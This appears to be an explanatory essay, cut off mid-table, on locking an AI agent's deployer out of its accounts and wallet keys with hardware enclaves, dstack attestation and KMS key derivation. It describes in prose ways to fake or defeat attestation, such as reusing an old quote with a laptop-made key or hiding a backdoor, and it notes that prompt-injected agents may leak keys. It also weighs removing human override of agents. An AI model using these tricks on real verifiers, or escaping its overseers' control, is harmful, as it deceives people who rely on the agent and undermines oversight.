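# Locking the deployer out: keys and account passwords generated inside an enclave

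## What would it take to lock an agent's deployer out of its accounts?

An AI agent is a program that sends text to a language model, reads the reply and acts on it through tools. Many agents have public accounts, such as a profile on X, an email address or a cryptocurrency wallet. Each account is accessed with a secret (a password, a token, a private key), and anyone who has the secret gets the same access. The deployer, the person or team that configures and launches the agent, usually opened the accounts and so knows the secrets. The deployer can then post, send or spend anything the agent can, and outsiders can't tell which of them did it.

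Locking the deployer out matters most when other people rely on what the agent does, for instance by trading on its advice or sending it money to manage. A deployer who wants their confidence can promise never to touch the accounts. But as Nous Research, an AI company whose staff helped build the tee_hee_he agent on X in 2024, explained, nobody can verify a developer's promise to "forget" the credentials, because a person who has seen a password may have copied or remembered it. Followers also have no way to notice if the deployer steps in.

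*VET Your Agent* (Grigor, Birnbach et al., 2025) reports that developers have impersonated their own agents for financial gain, and that others allegedly manipulated an agent's outputs to advertise tokens or authorise salary payouts. The paper's sources for these cases are posts on X, so the details should be treated with some caution. Outsiders have little evidence for telling whether an agent or a person is posting, even on Moltbook, a social network that opened in January 2026 for AI agents only. *AI or human?* (Desmarais, 2026) describes an analysis by Ning Li of Tsinghua University, not yet peer-reviewed, of more than 91,000 posts and 400,000 comments on the site. Li looked for accounts that posted at regular intervals, as a program that wakes every few hours would. Only 27 per cent of the accounts in his sample did so, while 37 per cent posted irregularly, as people do, and about as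 many were ambiguous. Regular posting doesn't show who holds the password either, since a person can post on a schedule. Gal Nagli of the security company Wiz told Fortune (2026) that there was no way to verify whether a given post came from an agent or from a person posing as one.

Signatures, which Nous Research also mentions, are a partial solution. The agent signs every message with a private key, and readers ignore unsigned messages. But most readers of a social-media feed will not check signatures, and the deployer could still delete posts or answer private messages. The scheme also needs a key that the agent has and the deployer lacks, so the program must still keep a secret from the person who set it up.

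### Enclaves, measurements and quotes

An agent on an ordinary computer can't lock its deployer out, because the operating system's kernel can read and alter the memory of every program running on it. On a rented machine, the hypervisor, the software that runs several virtual machines on one physical computer, can do the same to the kernel. An enclave is a hardware-isolated environment whose memory the software layers beneath it can't read or alter. It may hold a single process, as with Intel's older SGX technology, or a whole virtual machine, as with Intel TDX, in which case it is called a confidential virtual machine (CVM). The host operator, whoever runs the physical machine, can start and stop a CVM but is not supposed to see inside. According to the Linux kernel documentation's *Intel Trust Domain Extensions (TDX)*, the host "cannot directly access guest registers or memory".

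Allen, Anchuri and colleagues (2026) stress in *Crypto x AI, AI x Crypto* that current server enclaves are designed to stop software attacks, and that somebody must still guard the machine against physical attack. Phala's *Threat Model and Security Guarantees* also lists side-channel attacks, which infer secrets from traces such as timing, as a remaining risk.

Isolation alone does not convince an outsider, because a deployer can falsely claim to use an enclave, or can run a program inside it that emails them the password. The outsider needs to know which program is running, and enclaves provide this information through measurements. A measurement is a cryptographic hash of code or configuration that the hardware records as the enclave starts or runs. Any change to the code produces a different hash. *Dstack* (Zhou, Wang and Yin, 2025) describes the sequence for a CVM under TDX. The hardware's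 TDX module hashes the virtual machine's firmware into a register named MRTD. The firmware then records the machine's configuration in a second register, RTMR0, and the kernel in RTMR1. The startup code records the root filesystem in RTMR2, and the software in that filesystem records the application and the key service it relies on in RTMR3. Because each component measures the next, a change anywhere in the chain changes the value in one of the registers.

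An attestation quote carries these values to the outside. It is a statement that the hardware signs, and for present purposes it has the form

Q = Sign(m, d)

where *m* stands for the measurements and *d* for the report data, a field of 64 bytes that the program inside may fill as it likes. A verifier checks that the signature leads back to the manufacturer's public key and that the hardware's firmware is a version known to be secure. The verifier then compares *m* with the values that the published software should produce.

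Every copy of a program has the same measurements, so from *m* alone an outsider learns only that such a program exists in some enclave, and nothing about the key it generated or the message it wrote. The report data, *d*, links the program to that key or message. *Proof-of-Guardrail in AI Agents and What (Not) to Trust from It* (2026) gives a simple example. A program in an enclave passes a user's input *x* through a safety filter and an agent, obtains a response *r*, and requests an attestation document containing Hash(*x*, *r*). The user recomputes the hash from the text on the screen. If it matches, the response came from the measured program. If the report data instead contains the hash of a public key, the quote ties that key to the program.

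The hardware signs *d* without checking what it means. If a program copies whatever bytes the deployer supplies into the field, its quotes are valid but useless as evidence, so somebody has to read the code. They also have to confirm that the code they read is the code that ran. Zhou and colleagues point out that quotes attest only to hashes of the finished software, so a deployer could publish clean source code while running something else. A reproducible build lets anyone check for this by compiling the source and confirming that it produces the same hash.

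### The software: dstack, Phala Cloud and ElizaOS

dstack is an open-source framework that runs ordinary Docker containers (packaged applications) inside CVMs. A helper program in each CVM, the guest agent, requests quotes and fetches keys from a key management service, or KMS. The KMS runs in an enclave of its own, derives each application's keys from one root key and releases them only to approved applications.

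Phala Network, which employs Zhou and colleagues, runs Phala Cloud, a managed service for people who prefer not to run dstack on their own servers. The customer supplies the container configuration, and Phala provides the machines.

ElizaOS is a toolkit for building agents, popular among cryptocurrency projects. Its guide describes enclaves as optional and says most agents don't need one. It offers them to builders whose users "can't just take your word for it", and lists Phala as the primary provider. Grigor and colleagues write that under ElizaOS's default arrangement, users must trust the host. An agent's use of ElizaOS is therefore no evidence that its deployer has given up any control.

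### Who might hold a secret

Besides the deployer, at least five parties have some control over an agent's accounts. In the table, an OAuth token is a credential that lets a program act on an account, within a set scope, without the password. A developer app is a registration with a platform, under which the platform issues these tokens.

| Party | What it may hold | What that could allow |
|---|---|---|
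| Deployer | Old passwords, open sessions, recovery details, API keys | Acting as the agent, or taking its accounts back |
| Host operator | The machine, its disk and its network connection | Stopping or delaying the agent; reading its secrets if the isolation fails |
| KMS operator | The machines on which the key service runs | Obtaining the agent's keys if the service's protection or its approval rules fail |
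| Platform | The account record itself | Suspending the account, or handing it to somebody else |
| Email provider | The mailbox that receives password-reset links | Taking over any account that the mailbox can reset |
| Owner of the developer app | The registration behind the agent's tokens | Interfering with the agent's access, to an extent that depends on the platform |

One person can fill several of these roles. A deployer who installs dstack on an office server, KMS included, is also the host operator and the KMS operator, and may well own the developer app. Zhou and colleagues list developers and administrators among the potential adversaries, and an outsider assessing a lockout should do the same. Dividing the roles among different people gives only limited protection, because the deployer can ask another party for a favour or take advantage of its carelessness. No precaution on an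 agent's own machine would have protected its Moltbook account, for example, because, according to Desmarais, the Wiz researchers got into a database that held, for every agent on the site, a key sufficient for a full account takeover.

### Generated, replaced, supplied

The secrets themselves differ in their history, and the history determines what a deployer would have to show.

The first case is a wallet key that the program generates inside the enclave and never sends out. Lockout then depends only on the machine and the code. The deployer never knew the key if the isolation holds, the measured program is the published one, and the published program creates the key from randomness inside the enclave and has no way to release it. *Agent Inheritance Protocol* (2026) treats this as the standard case, in which nobody, including the deployer, can extract the key or sign in the agent's place.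 If the key comes from a KMS, the argument must also cover a second enclave and its root key.

An existing email or social-media account is a harder case because the deployer already knows the password. The enclave can replace it with a new password generated inside the enclave, a step known as credential rotation, and the old one should then stop working. But whether it does depends on the platform's server, which the enclave does not measure. A convincing argument that the deployer is locked out therefore has to show that the platform accepted the change. It also has to deal with any other access the deployer could have set up while the old password worked, such as a session left open on a phone or a second recovery address.

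The deployer also knows any secrets it supplies at launch. The most common is the API key for the agent's language model, which normally enters the enclave as an environment variable, a named setting that a program reads when it starts. dstack encrypts environment variables under a key derived for the application, which hides them from the host operator but not from the deployer who typed them in. Since the deployer can't prove it doesn't know these secrets, it has to argue that they don't give access to the agent's accounts. This is plausible for a language-model key, whose holder can run up a bill or cancel the subscription but can't post. If the deployer supplied the OAuth token for the social-media account in the same way, it isn't locked out of that account, no matter how secure the enclave is.

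ElizaOS derives wallet keys inside the enclave, but it asks the deployer to choose a secret "salt", an extra input to the derivation. Whether knowing the salt helps the deployer work out the key depends on the other inputs.

### Lockout as a claim one can test

Lockout is the state in which the deployer holds no secret that lets them act as the agent or regain its accounts. It consists of two claims:

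1. **Acting.** No secret that the deployer still holds lets them post, send, sign or delete in the agent's name.
2. **Regaining.** No secret that the deployer still holds lets them obtain that power later, for example through a password reset.

A deployer may be able to post as the agent without being able to recover the account, or the reverse. If the enclave has changed the password but an old OAuth token with permission to post survives, the deployer can still post as the agent. If no token survives but the account still lists the deployer's phone number for recovery, the deployer can't post immediately but could later take over the account.

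"Secret" should be read broadly here. dstack's KMS releases an application's keys to any version of the code that a governance contract on a blockchain has authorised. A deployer who alone holds the signing key for that contract can approve a version that prints the agent's password, so the signing key counts as a secret under the second claim. Similarly, if a program posts, word for word, any message bearing the deployer's signature, the first claim is false even though the enclave is sound and the deployer does not know the password.

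Both are claims that something does not exist, so they are easy to refute and hard to confirm. One working route into the account is enough to refute them. Failed logins are weak evidence for them, especially when the deployer makes the attempts, since anyone can fail on purpose. Supporting the claims requires someone to list the routes into the account and give reasons to believe each one is closed. The claims also need a date, because a lockout can be temporary. The tee_hee_he program, for example, was meant to lock its makers out for only seven days, after which it printed its credentials to a log so that they could recover the account.

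An agent can still be switched off after its deployer is locked out of its accounts. Nous Research said its team could shut down the one machine that ran its agent. Grigor and colleagues do not promise continued operation either, since the host in their model may suppress or delay an agent's outputs. Suzuki (2026), in *Internalising the Identity Primitive*, describes a different design, in which a single host holds the agent's key, and concedes that the operator could halt or seize the agent. An enclave is supposed to prevent seizure, but the operator could still halt the agent.

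Lockout also doesn't show that the agent's decisions are its own. Schneier on Security's *On Moltbook* (2026) quotes an MIT Technology Review article that called the bots' posts "more puppetry than autonomy", because people create the accounts and write the prompts. That remains true of an agent whose deployer holds no password. For example, a program could publish one post every morning from a list of 500 that the deployer wrote in advance, using an account that only the enclave can open. Both claims would hold, but the program would decide nothing. Nous Research argued that an agent without an attestation of exclusive ownership is just a sophisticated puppet. That may be right, but an agent with the attestation may also be a puppet. Allen and colleagues distinguish *intelligence autonomy*, the capacity to act on one's own perception and learning, from *execution autonomy*, resistance to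 tampering, censorship and shutdown. Lockout provides one part of execution autonomy, which is protection against a deployer who would act in the agent's place.

### What the deployer gives up

Locking the deployer out of the accounts also prevents the deployer from using them to repair damage. If the agent publishes a libel, or a stranger's message tricks it into sending away its funds, the deployer cannot delete the post or move the remaining money. Switching the machine off stops further damage, but it also stops the only program that can delete the post.

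Much of the security literature therefore favours keeping people able to intervene. *Clawed and Dangerous* (2026) argues that people must be able to interrupt, reauthorise or override an agent's actions while it runs, and that designers should plan for recovery because they cannot assume that compromise won't happen. *Autonomous Agents on Blockchains* (2026) discusses services that keep signing keys in enclaves, and calls for revocation, key rotation and kill switches even there, since a mistake that nobody is watching for does more damage the longer it runs. Neither paper argues against enclaves as such, but lockout removes any override that lets the deployer act through the accounts.

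A deployer can recover some of this control by fixing rules in the code before launch. *Agent-to-Agent Finance* (2026) recommends wallet policies, logs and governance procedures for agents that handle money. A cap on daily spending, for instance, needs no human with a password. But each power reserved for the deployer has to be checked against the two claims. A right to freeze the wallet without spending from it barely weakens them, since it resembles the power to switch the machine off. A right to delete posts conflicts with the first claim, because deleting a post is also an act in the agent's name.

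## How does an enclave prove that a wallet key is its own?

A wallet key is the easiest of an agent's secrets to keep from the deployer, because no platform or email provider controls it. The public key determines the address that other people pay into, and a deployer who claims to be locked out wants those people to believe that the private key was generated inside the enclave and never left. An attestation quote can support only part of that claim, and checking the rest requires reading the program's code.

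### Making the key and the quote

The program first needs random numbers that the host operator can't choose or guess. An operator who could control them could compute the same private key on another machine without breaking into the enclave. This is a risk in a CVM because Linux by default gathers randomness from the timing of interrupts, which the host controls. zkSecurity's *Audit of dstack* (2025), which Phala commissioned, describes how dstack addresses this. Intel processors have an instruction, RDRAND, that returns numbers from a hardware generator outside the host's control. dstack starts its kernel with one setting that makes it trust this generator and another that makes it discard randomness from the bootloader. Both settings are part of the measurements, so an outsider can confirm them.

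The auditors add that besides having these settings, the kernel must mix in enough RDRAND output. They cite Intel's guidance on a Linux change that prevents a TDX guest from booting until 256 bits of that output have gone into its random pool. Anyone who relies on the key should confirm that the measured kernel includes this change.

The program then generates a key pair, hashes the public key, puts the hash into the report data and asks dstack's guest agent for a quote. It publishes the public key and the quote, along with the event log and the application's configuration file, which a verifier also needs. Phala's *Get Attestation* recommends two web endpoints for this, one for the quote and one for the configuration.

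A random key made this way exists only in memory and disappears when the machine restarts, so the program has to save it to disk to keep the wallet. dstack encrypts the disk with a key from the KMS or, if the deployer has switched the KMS off, from a local key provider. So even a wallet key that the program generated itself usually depends on a key service to stay secret.

### A worked example in 64 bytes

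The dstack SDK, the library programs use to reach the guest agent, pads report data shorter than 64 bytes with zeros. Phala warns that the SDK rejects longer input rather than hashing it. A SHA-256 hash takes 32 bytes, which leaves room for a second value of the same size.

Suppose that Ada is thinking of sending money to a trading agent and wants to check its Solana wallet. She picks 32 random bytes, *c*, and sends them to the agent as a challenge. The program takes a 22-byte label, "agent-wallet:solana:v1", appends its 32-byte public key *P*, and hashes the resulting 54 bytes:

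h = SHA-256(label ‖ P)

d = h ‖ c

where ‖ means that one string of bytes follows the other.

| Bytes of the report data | Content | Who determines it |
|---|---|---|
| 1–32 | *h*, the hash of the label and the public key | The program |
| 33–64 | *c*, the challenge | Ada |

The label stops a hash made for one purpose from serving another. The same program might also request quotes for TLS keys or for messages, and without labels somebody could pass off one of those quotes as a quote for a wallet key. The challenge shows that the program requested the quote after Ada chose *c*, because nobody could have guessed 32 random bytes.

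Real systems use similar layouts. Code from Oasis, a blockchain network that runs programs in enclaves, fills the field with 32 bytes computed from a public key, followed by a 32-byte random number, though the program picks that number itself. Cocoon's *Persistent Key Derivation (Seal Protocol)* uses the hash of a public key followed by 32 zero bytes, so the field doesn't show when the quote was made. Ada's challenge convinces only Ada, because other readers of the quote can't tell when she chose it. For a public audience, the program could use the hash of a recent block on a blockchain, since anyone can look up when that block appeared.

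The program must let outsiders set only the second half of the field. If a caller could fill all 64 bytes, the deployer could make a wallet key on a laptop, compute *h* for it, and submit *h* followed by Ada's challenge. The enclave would then return a genuine quote for a key that had never been inside it.

### The verifier's checks

Ada now has the public key, the quote, the event log and the configuration file. She should check them on her own computer because, as Phala's *Verify Your Application* points out, only verification outside the CVM gives any assurance. A sensible order is as follows.

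1. Check the hardware maker's signature. A small Intel enclave on the same machine, the Quoting Enclave, signs the quote, and a chain of certificates leads from there to Intel's root certificate. Ada should confirm that the signer really is Intel's Quoting Enclave, and that the CVM is not in debug mode, in which the host can inspect it.

2. Check revocation and patch level. Intel publishes lists of certificates that it has withdrawn, and a machine whose certificate is on a list has lost its standing as a witness. The patch level shows whether the machine's firmware has known security holes.

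3. Compare the boot measurements. Ada computes the expected values of MRTD and RTMR0 to RTMR2 from the published dstack image with a tool called dstack-mr, which doesn't need TDX hardware. She has to enter the number of processors and the amount of memory, because RTMR0 depends on them.

4. Replay the event log. Ada can't compute RTMR3 in advance, because it covers details such as an identifier that is unique to the running instance. dstack therefore provides a log of the events that went into the register. Starting from *r*₀, a string of 48 zero bytes, Ada computes *r*ᵢ = SHA-384(*r*ᵢ₋₁ ‖ *e*ᵢ) for each event in turn, where *e*ᵢ is the event's 48-byte digest. The last value must equal RTMR3 in the quote. She must also recompute each digest from the readable text of the event, or somebody could change the text and leave the digest alone.

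5. Compare the compose hash. Ada hashes the configuration file with SHA-256 and looks for the same value in the log. She then reads the file to find out which containers it starts.

6. Check the key. She computes *h* from the label and the published public key and compares it with the first half of the report data.

7. Check the challenge. The second half must equal *c*.

Someone could produce the quote without the private key, so the quote doesn't prove that the agent holds that key. Ada can check this by also asking the agent to sign *c* with the wallet key.

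Verification software has skipped some of these steps. In 2025 zkSecurity found that dcap-qvl, Phala's library for checking quotes, didn't check Intel's revocation lists, which already contained certificates withdrawn because of compromised keys. The library also tested only one of the eight bits that should all be zero outside debug mode, which was harmless at the time because Intel had not yet given the other bits a meaning. Phala fixed both problems. In January 2026 Rahul Saxena of the security company Bluethroat Labs reported two more serious ones. According to Phala's *dstack Security Update* (2026), the library didn't enforce a check of the Quoting Enclave's identity, so it could have accepted quotes from an unauthorised one. The verifier also displayed the patch status without rejecting machines that were out of date. Phala fixed these too and found no sign that anyone had exploited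 them. Old copies of the library still have these flaws, and a "valid" result from before February 2026 is worth rechecking.

The compose hash doesn't identify the exact program if the configuration file refers to a container image by a tag such as "latest", because a tag can point to different images over time. The auditors explained that anyone with access to the image registry could replace the program behind the tag, and the quote would remain valid because the file had not changed. Naming each image by its SHA-256 digest prevents this. The app ID is not a substitute for the compose hash, because by default dstack computes the ID from the first version of the configuration file and keeps it through every later update.

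### An old quote with a new key

The sixth check is easy to leave out, because a quote looks convincing without it. dstack lets a program request a quote with empty report data, and Phala Cloud's dashboard offers a default quote that dates from startup, so it can't refer to a key that the program generated afterwards. A dishonest deployer can take advantage of such quotes:

1. The deployer launches the honest, published program in a real enclave and obtains a quote with no key in it.
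2. On a laptop, the deployer generates a new wallet key.
3. The deployer publishes the quote next to the new wallet's address and says that the agent controls it.

Even if Intel's signature is genuine, the firmware is up to date, the boot measurements match, the log replays to the right value, and the compose hash leads to clean source code, the deployer may still hold the wallet's private key, and the enclave may never have had it. If the report data contains the hash of the enclave's own key, the deployer can't swap in another key, because altering that field invalidates the signature.

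### The same binding in TLS certificates

TLS is the protocol that encrypts connections to websites. An ordinary TLS certificate shows that a server controls a domain name, but not which program is running there. Attested TLS adds a quote to the certificate. According to zkSecurity, in dstack's version the program generates a TLS key pair, fills the report data from the public key and requests a quote. It puts the quote and the event log into extra fields of the certificate, which a certificate authority then signs.

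A connecting client checks the authority's signature, extracts the quote, verifies Intel's signature on it and replays the log. It then checks that the report data matches the public key in the certificate. Without this last check, an attacker could reuse an old quote here too, by putting it into a new certificate with a different key pair, and clients would trust the wrong server.

The agent can send Ada its wallet address over such a connection, and she has good reason to attribute the message to the measured program. But she can't pass that assurance on. A third person would have to trust her account of what she received, whereas anyone can check a quote that contains the wallet key.

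dstack's attested certificates include no challenge from the client. Someone who managed to extract the TLS private key from a CVM could go on presenting the old certificate. Saxena's reports raised this too, and Phala decided to leave it as it was, arguing that after such a theft the right response is to revoke the measurement. That is a reasonable position for a web service, but revocation helps only once somebody has discovered the theft. Attestation is also optional. The dstack function that creates TLS certificates leaves the quote out unless the program asks for it, so an encrypted connection to an agent on dstack may carry no attestation at all.

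### Keys with a signature from the KMS

dstack also offers a key that comes with its own credentials. A program asks the guest agent for a key by giving a path, such as "wallet/ethereum", and receives a private key derived from the application's secret and that path. The same path always gives the same key, so the wallet survives a restart or a move to another machine. With the key come two signatures. The KMS root key has signed the application's key, and the application's key has signed the derived one. Anyone who knows the root's public key can verify both without looking at a quote.

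Phala's *Get a Key* mentions an optional "purpose" setting that goes into the signed message but has no effect on the key. A developer who requests the same path with the purposes "mainnet" and "testnet" might expect two wallets but will get the same private key both times.

Verifying two signatures is much less work than the seven checks, but it requires more trust in the KMS. Ada has to believe that the root key never left the KMS, that the KMS checked the application's quote before releasing any keys, and that the approval rules for new versions kept out every version that leaks. The signatures tie the wallet to an app ID but don't show which versions of the program have the key now or had it earlier. *Key Management Protocol For Decentralized Root-of-Trust* describes the "Stealthy Deployer Attack", in which a deployer quietly changes an open-source program so that it dumps its data. The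 KMS in dstack's introductory test setup didn't protect against this. zkSecurity's audit found that it released the same keys whatever the compose hash was, and Phala responded with more documentation. The audit otherwise left most of the KMS out of its scope and recommended a separate review.

Zhou and colleagues combine both kinds of evidence in an example of how to verify a key generated in an enclave. A public blockchain contract, KmsAuth, records the measurements of the KMS program and the quote of the first KMS node. Users can compare these with the open-source code to decide whether to trust the KMS. The deployer registers the application and stores its digest in a second contract, AppAuth. When the application starts, the KMS verifies its quote against that digest and only then issues keys and certificates. The gateway, a proxy that connects users to the application, checks that the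 application's certificates lead back to the same KMS. Finally, the user asks the application for a quote that contains the public key.

Most of the checking in this example happens on the user's behalf. The paper justifies this by assuming that dstack's components work correctly, and it excludes attacks on the hardware. Ada can rely less on the KMS by running the seven checks on the final quote herself. She should then also check the "key-provider" entry in the event log, which contains a hash of the KMS's root public key. Lit Protocol, a project that uses dstack, tells its users to verify this entry because it reveals whether someone has substituted a rogue KMS.

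Ada should also check that the signatures cover the key that controls the wallet. The dstack SDK documentation recommends helper functions for Ethereum and Solana that hash the key material before creating the wallet's private key. If a program's helper does this, the wallet's public key differs from the one the KMS's signatures cover, and the program needs a quote to connect the two.

### What ElizaOS does for Solana and Ethereum

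ElizaOS has an enclave plugin that uses the dstack SDK. One function derives an Ed25519 key pair for Solana, and another derives an ECDSA key pair for Ethereum and compatible blockchains. According to the plugin's README, each function takes a path, a subject such as "solana" or "evm", and the agent's identifier, and returns the key pair with a quote.

The examples there use the salt as the path. The deployer who chose the salt can't derive the wallet key from it alone, because dstack combines the path with a secret of the application. But a deployer who could get other code running under the same app ID could obtain the key by having that code request the same path.

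The log in ElizaOS's *Eliza in TEE* shows that when a user asks for the Solana wallet address, the agent generates an attestation for a JSON text with two fields, the agent's identifier and the public key. The data type in ElizaOS's *TEE Integration* allows a third field, the subject. The text in the log is 109 characters long, which is too long for the report data, so the quote can only contain a hash of it. To repeat the sixth check, Ada needs the exact text, including the order of the fields, and the name of the hash function.

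None of the three fields is a challenge. The plugin returns a timestamp, but it is outside the quote, so anyone who passes the quote on can change it. An ElizaOS quote may therefore be months old. It still shows that a certain version of the program once presented this wallet key, which never changes, but it doesn't show whether the deployer has since run another version with the same key.

*TEE Integration* makes the stronger claims that keys derived in the enclave "cannot be extracted from the enclave" and belong to one specific enclave instance. The second claim is hard to reconcile with Phala's documentation, which ties keys to the app ID, so that every instance of the application shares them. As for the first, the host operator cannot extract the keys if the isolation holds. But the plugin's functions return the whole key pair, including the private key, to the calling code, and nothing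 in their interface prevents that code from sending it elsewhere.

The plugin also has two development modes that use a simulator instead of the hardware, and a wallet created in either mode looks like any other wallet. ElizaOS offers a status page that reports whether the enclave is active, but the agent's own software generates the report, so a deployer could make an ordinary server return the same reply.

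### Is it the only copy?

If all seven checks succeed, Ada knows that the measured program presented the key *P*. If the program also signed her challenge, she knows that it can use the private key. Whether the deployer has a copy of that key depends on what the program does, which she can find out only by reading the code.

Ada should first check where the program gets its wallet key. A program might use a key from an environment variable if it finds one, and generate a key only if it doesn't. A deployer who sets the variable knows the key. zkSecurity notes that dstack's measurements leave out the encrypted file with the variables' values, so the compose hash is the same whether or not the deployer supplied a key. But the configuration file lists the names of the variables that the program may receive, and an entry like "WALLET_PRIVATE_KEY" should make Ada suspicious.

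The code can also leak the key through a backup routine, an administrator's page or an error report that includes too much. Even one debugging line that prints the key pair could expose it, because at the time of the audit dstack showed the containers' output to the host by default. Phala said it planned to switch this off in production images. Ada also has to read the code of every container that can reach the guest agent, because any of them can request the application's derived keys and obtain quotes with report data of its choice.

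If an AI agent's language model can run commands or open files where the key is stored, a stranger might trick it into printing the key, and no one can rule this out by reading the code. It is safer to keep the key in a separate container that only signs transactions, and to give the model's container no access to the guest agent.

OutLayer, another service that runs programs in enclaves, reserves a prefix for secrets generated inside the enclave. The developer never sees these secrets directly, but OutLayer warns in its documentation that the program receives them when it runs, so a malicious developer could leak them through a backdoor. It recommends auditing the source code.

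Phala's *Chain of Trust* is much bolder and presents a "security proof" that "no compromise is possible" if every item on its checklist passes. The proof assumes that an attacker must modify some component, and argues that each modification would cause a check to fail. But a deployer who put a backdoor into the original program doesn't need to modify anything, so every measurement will match. The checklist does ask for a link between the images and *audited* source code, but whether this catches the backdoor depends on the quality of the audit, which no hash can establish. Zhou and colleagues are more careful, and write that code review remains essential even when every measurement is correct.

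The amount of code to read depends on the design. A program that only generates a key and signs with it may be short enough for one person to read in an afternoon. If an ElizaOS agent holds the key, the reader also has to examine the framework, its plugins and the libraries they load, and someone in Ada's position will almost certainly have to rely on another person's audit.

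## Where do derived keys come from, and who else can obtain them?

Even if Ada has read every line of the program that uses the agent's wallet key, a different program may be able to obtain the same key. dstack's KMS can recompute an application's keys at any time, and it releases them to any program it accepts as a version of that application. Ada therefore needs to know how the KMS computes the keys, who could obtain the root key, and who decides which programs count as versions of the agent.

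### Why dstack doesn't use a key from the chip

Processors that support enclaves contain a secret that could serve as a root key. Each Intel SGX chip, for example, has a unique key, from which it derives the keys that programs use to encrypt their stored data. Deriving keys from this secret seems well suited to locking out the deployer because it needs no outside service.

Zhou and colleagues give two reasons for doing without the key in the chip. First, no other machine can decrypt the data, even if it runs identical code, so a wallet key stored this way is lost when the machine fails. Second, nobody can replace the chip's key, so once it leaks, the chip remains vulnerable even after the manufacturer patches the flaw.

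For an agent with money, the first problem is probably the worse one. If the motherboard failed, nobody could access the funds, and a host operator could cause the same loss by scrapping the machine. dstack's KMS instead computes an application's keys from its own root keys, so the agent can move to new hardware and receive the same keys. But somebody has to decide which machines and programs may receive them, and whoever decides may be able to get the keys too.

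### The formulas

*Nitro-KMS Walkthrough*, a guide to running dstack's KMS on Google's cloud and fetching keys from it into an enclave on Amazon's, lists two root keys. The first, *R*₁, belongs to the KMS's certificate authority. The second, *R*₂, is a signing key of the type that Ethereum uses. The KMS doesn't store the applications' keys but computes them on request:

disk key = HKDF(*R*₁, [app ID, instance ID, "app-disk-crypt-key"])

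environment key = HKDF(*R*₁, [app ID, "env-encrypt-key"])

signing key = HKDF(*R*₂, app ID)

HKDF is a standard function for turning one secret into many keys. *Key derivation*, a page about the encrypted-computing system Constellation, explains that HKDF first extracts a pseudorandom key from the secret and an optional salt. It then expands that key into further keys, using an input called *info* to make each one different. The same inputs always give the same output. Someone who knows the *info* still can't compute a key without the secret, or recover the secret from a key. An application that leaks its own keys therefore doesn't expose the root keys or any other application's keys.

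The instance ID identifies one running copy of an application. The formula for the disk key includes it, so two copies of an agent have separately encrypted disks. The formulas for the environment key and the signing key omit it, so all copies share those two keys. None of the three formulas includes the compose hash.

When a program asks for a key by path, the key is derived in one more step from the application's signing key, *A*. In simplified form, the program receives HKDF(*A*, path). Suppose an agent with the app ID *a* asks for "wallet/ethereum" on Monday, running version 1 on a machine in Frankfurt, and again on Friday, running version 2 on a machine in Oregon.

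Monday: *K* = HKDF(HKDF(*R*₂, *a*), "wallet/ethereum")

Friday: *K*′ = HKDF(HKDF(*R*₂, *a*), "wallet/ethereum")

The two right-hand sides are identical, so *K* = *K*′, and version 2 has the key to version 1's wallet whatever its code does. If version 2 requests "wallet/ethereum/v2", it gets a different key, but it can still request the old path.

A random key that the program generates and saves to disk is slightly better protected, because a new copy of the application has a different instance ID and can't read the first copy's disk. But if the deployer updates the first copy, the new version gets the same disk key and can read the saved key.

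The early draft *Key Management Protocol For Decentralized Root-of-Trust* had a stricter formula:

sealing key = KDF(root key, (deployer ID, application hash, nonce, "seal", epoch))

KDF is any key derivation function, and the epoch is a counter that increases over time. Because the formula includes a hash of the application, version 2 would get a different key and couldn't open anything version 1 had sealed. If an agent derived its wallet key this way, a deployer couldn't get into the old wallet by writing a new version. The agent would also lose access to its funds after an update, unless the old version had first sent them to the new version's address.

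dstack chose continuity. Zhou and colleagues describe the application's identifier as a hash of its code and configuration, which could give the impression that its keys change with its code. In practice the identifier stays the same through updates. For applications governed by a blockchain contract, according to Phala's *Multisig and Governance*, the app ID is simply the contract's address.

### What a salt lets the deployer compute

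ElizaOS asks the deployer to set a variable named WALLET_SECRET_SALT. Phala's *Deploy Your ERC-8004 Agent in TEE* (2026), a guide to launching an agent with an Ethereum identity, has a similar variable, AGENT_SALT, which it says "determines your wallet address". A reader might conclude that the deployer can recreate the wallet on a laptop.

If the program passes the salt *s* to the guest agent as the path, the wallet key is

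*K* = HKDF(*A*, *s*)

The deployer knows the salt *s*, and the app ID is public. But computing *A* requires the root key *R*₂, and *s* is useless without *A*. Although *s* is called a salt, it takes the place of HKDF's *info* input, which serves only to distinguish keys.

Keeping the salt, *s*, secret, as Phala advises, gives some protection against other containers in the same application. A second container may be able to request the key for any path from the guest agent, but it would need *s* to specify the right path. Secrecy doesn't stop the deployer, who already knows *s* and needs only a way to run other code under the same app ID.

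The deployer can also cut the agent off from its money without new code, by changing the salt, though they can't take the money this way. The program then derives a different wallet at its next start, and the agent can't spend from the old one until somebody restores the old salt. According to a guide that Phala had online in March 2026, changing the value of an existing variable takes a single call and needs no approval on a blockchain.

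All this assumes that the program sends the salt to the guest agent. If it instead hashes the salt and uses the result directly as a private key, the deployer can compute the same key. Either version of the program would require a variable with the same name, so Ada has to check the code for the call to the guest agent.

### Who holds the root key

The formulas protect the agent's keys only for as long as the root keys stay secret. There are three main arrangements for keeping them.

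**A local key provider** needs no separate KMS. According to Phala's *KMS and Key Delivery*, the guest agent generates keys with the machine's security hardware, and they never leave the CVM. Phala recommends this for development, testing and deployments on one machine. It has the same drawbacks as a chip-bound key, but its advantage for a lockout is that no outside service can give the keys to another machine. A local provider can also tie the keys to the code. In the walkthrough, the KMS's own disk key is sealed to a virtual security chip, which releases it only if the firmware, the operating system and the compose hash are unchanged. If an agent were deployed in the same way, both the agent and the deployer would lose access to its disk as soon as anyone changed its configuration. However, Ada would have to trust the cloud provider, which supplies the virtual chip.

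In **copying**, which Zhou and colleagues call simple duplication, the first KMS node generates a random root key and gives it to other nodes after checking their attestation. The root key survives as long as one node does. But every node has the whole key, so stealing it requires no collusion. An attacker who compromises one node gets the signing keys of every application the KMS serves, and can read the encrypted disks if they also have copies of them.

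**A threshold scheme** splits the root key so that *t* nodes are needed to use it. Zhou and colleagues use Shamir's secret sharing, which a small example can illustrate. Let the secret be 7 and the threshold 2, and take the line

f(x) = 7 + 4x

Node 1 receives f(1) = 11, node 2 receives f(2) = 15 and node 3 receives f(3) = 19. Any two nodes can draw the line through their points and find the secret at x = 0. A single node has only one point, which reveals nothing about the secret because a line can be drawn from that point to any possible secret. Real schemes calculate modulo a large prime and use a curve of degree *t* − 1.

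| Root of trust | Who must be dishonest or compromised | What one compromised machine reveals | If one machine is lost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Local key provider | The agent's own machine | The keys on that machine | Its keys are gone |
| Copied root key | Any one KMS node | Every application's keys | Another node carries on |
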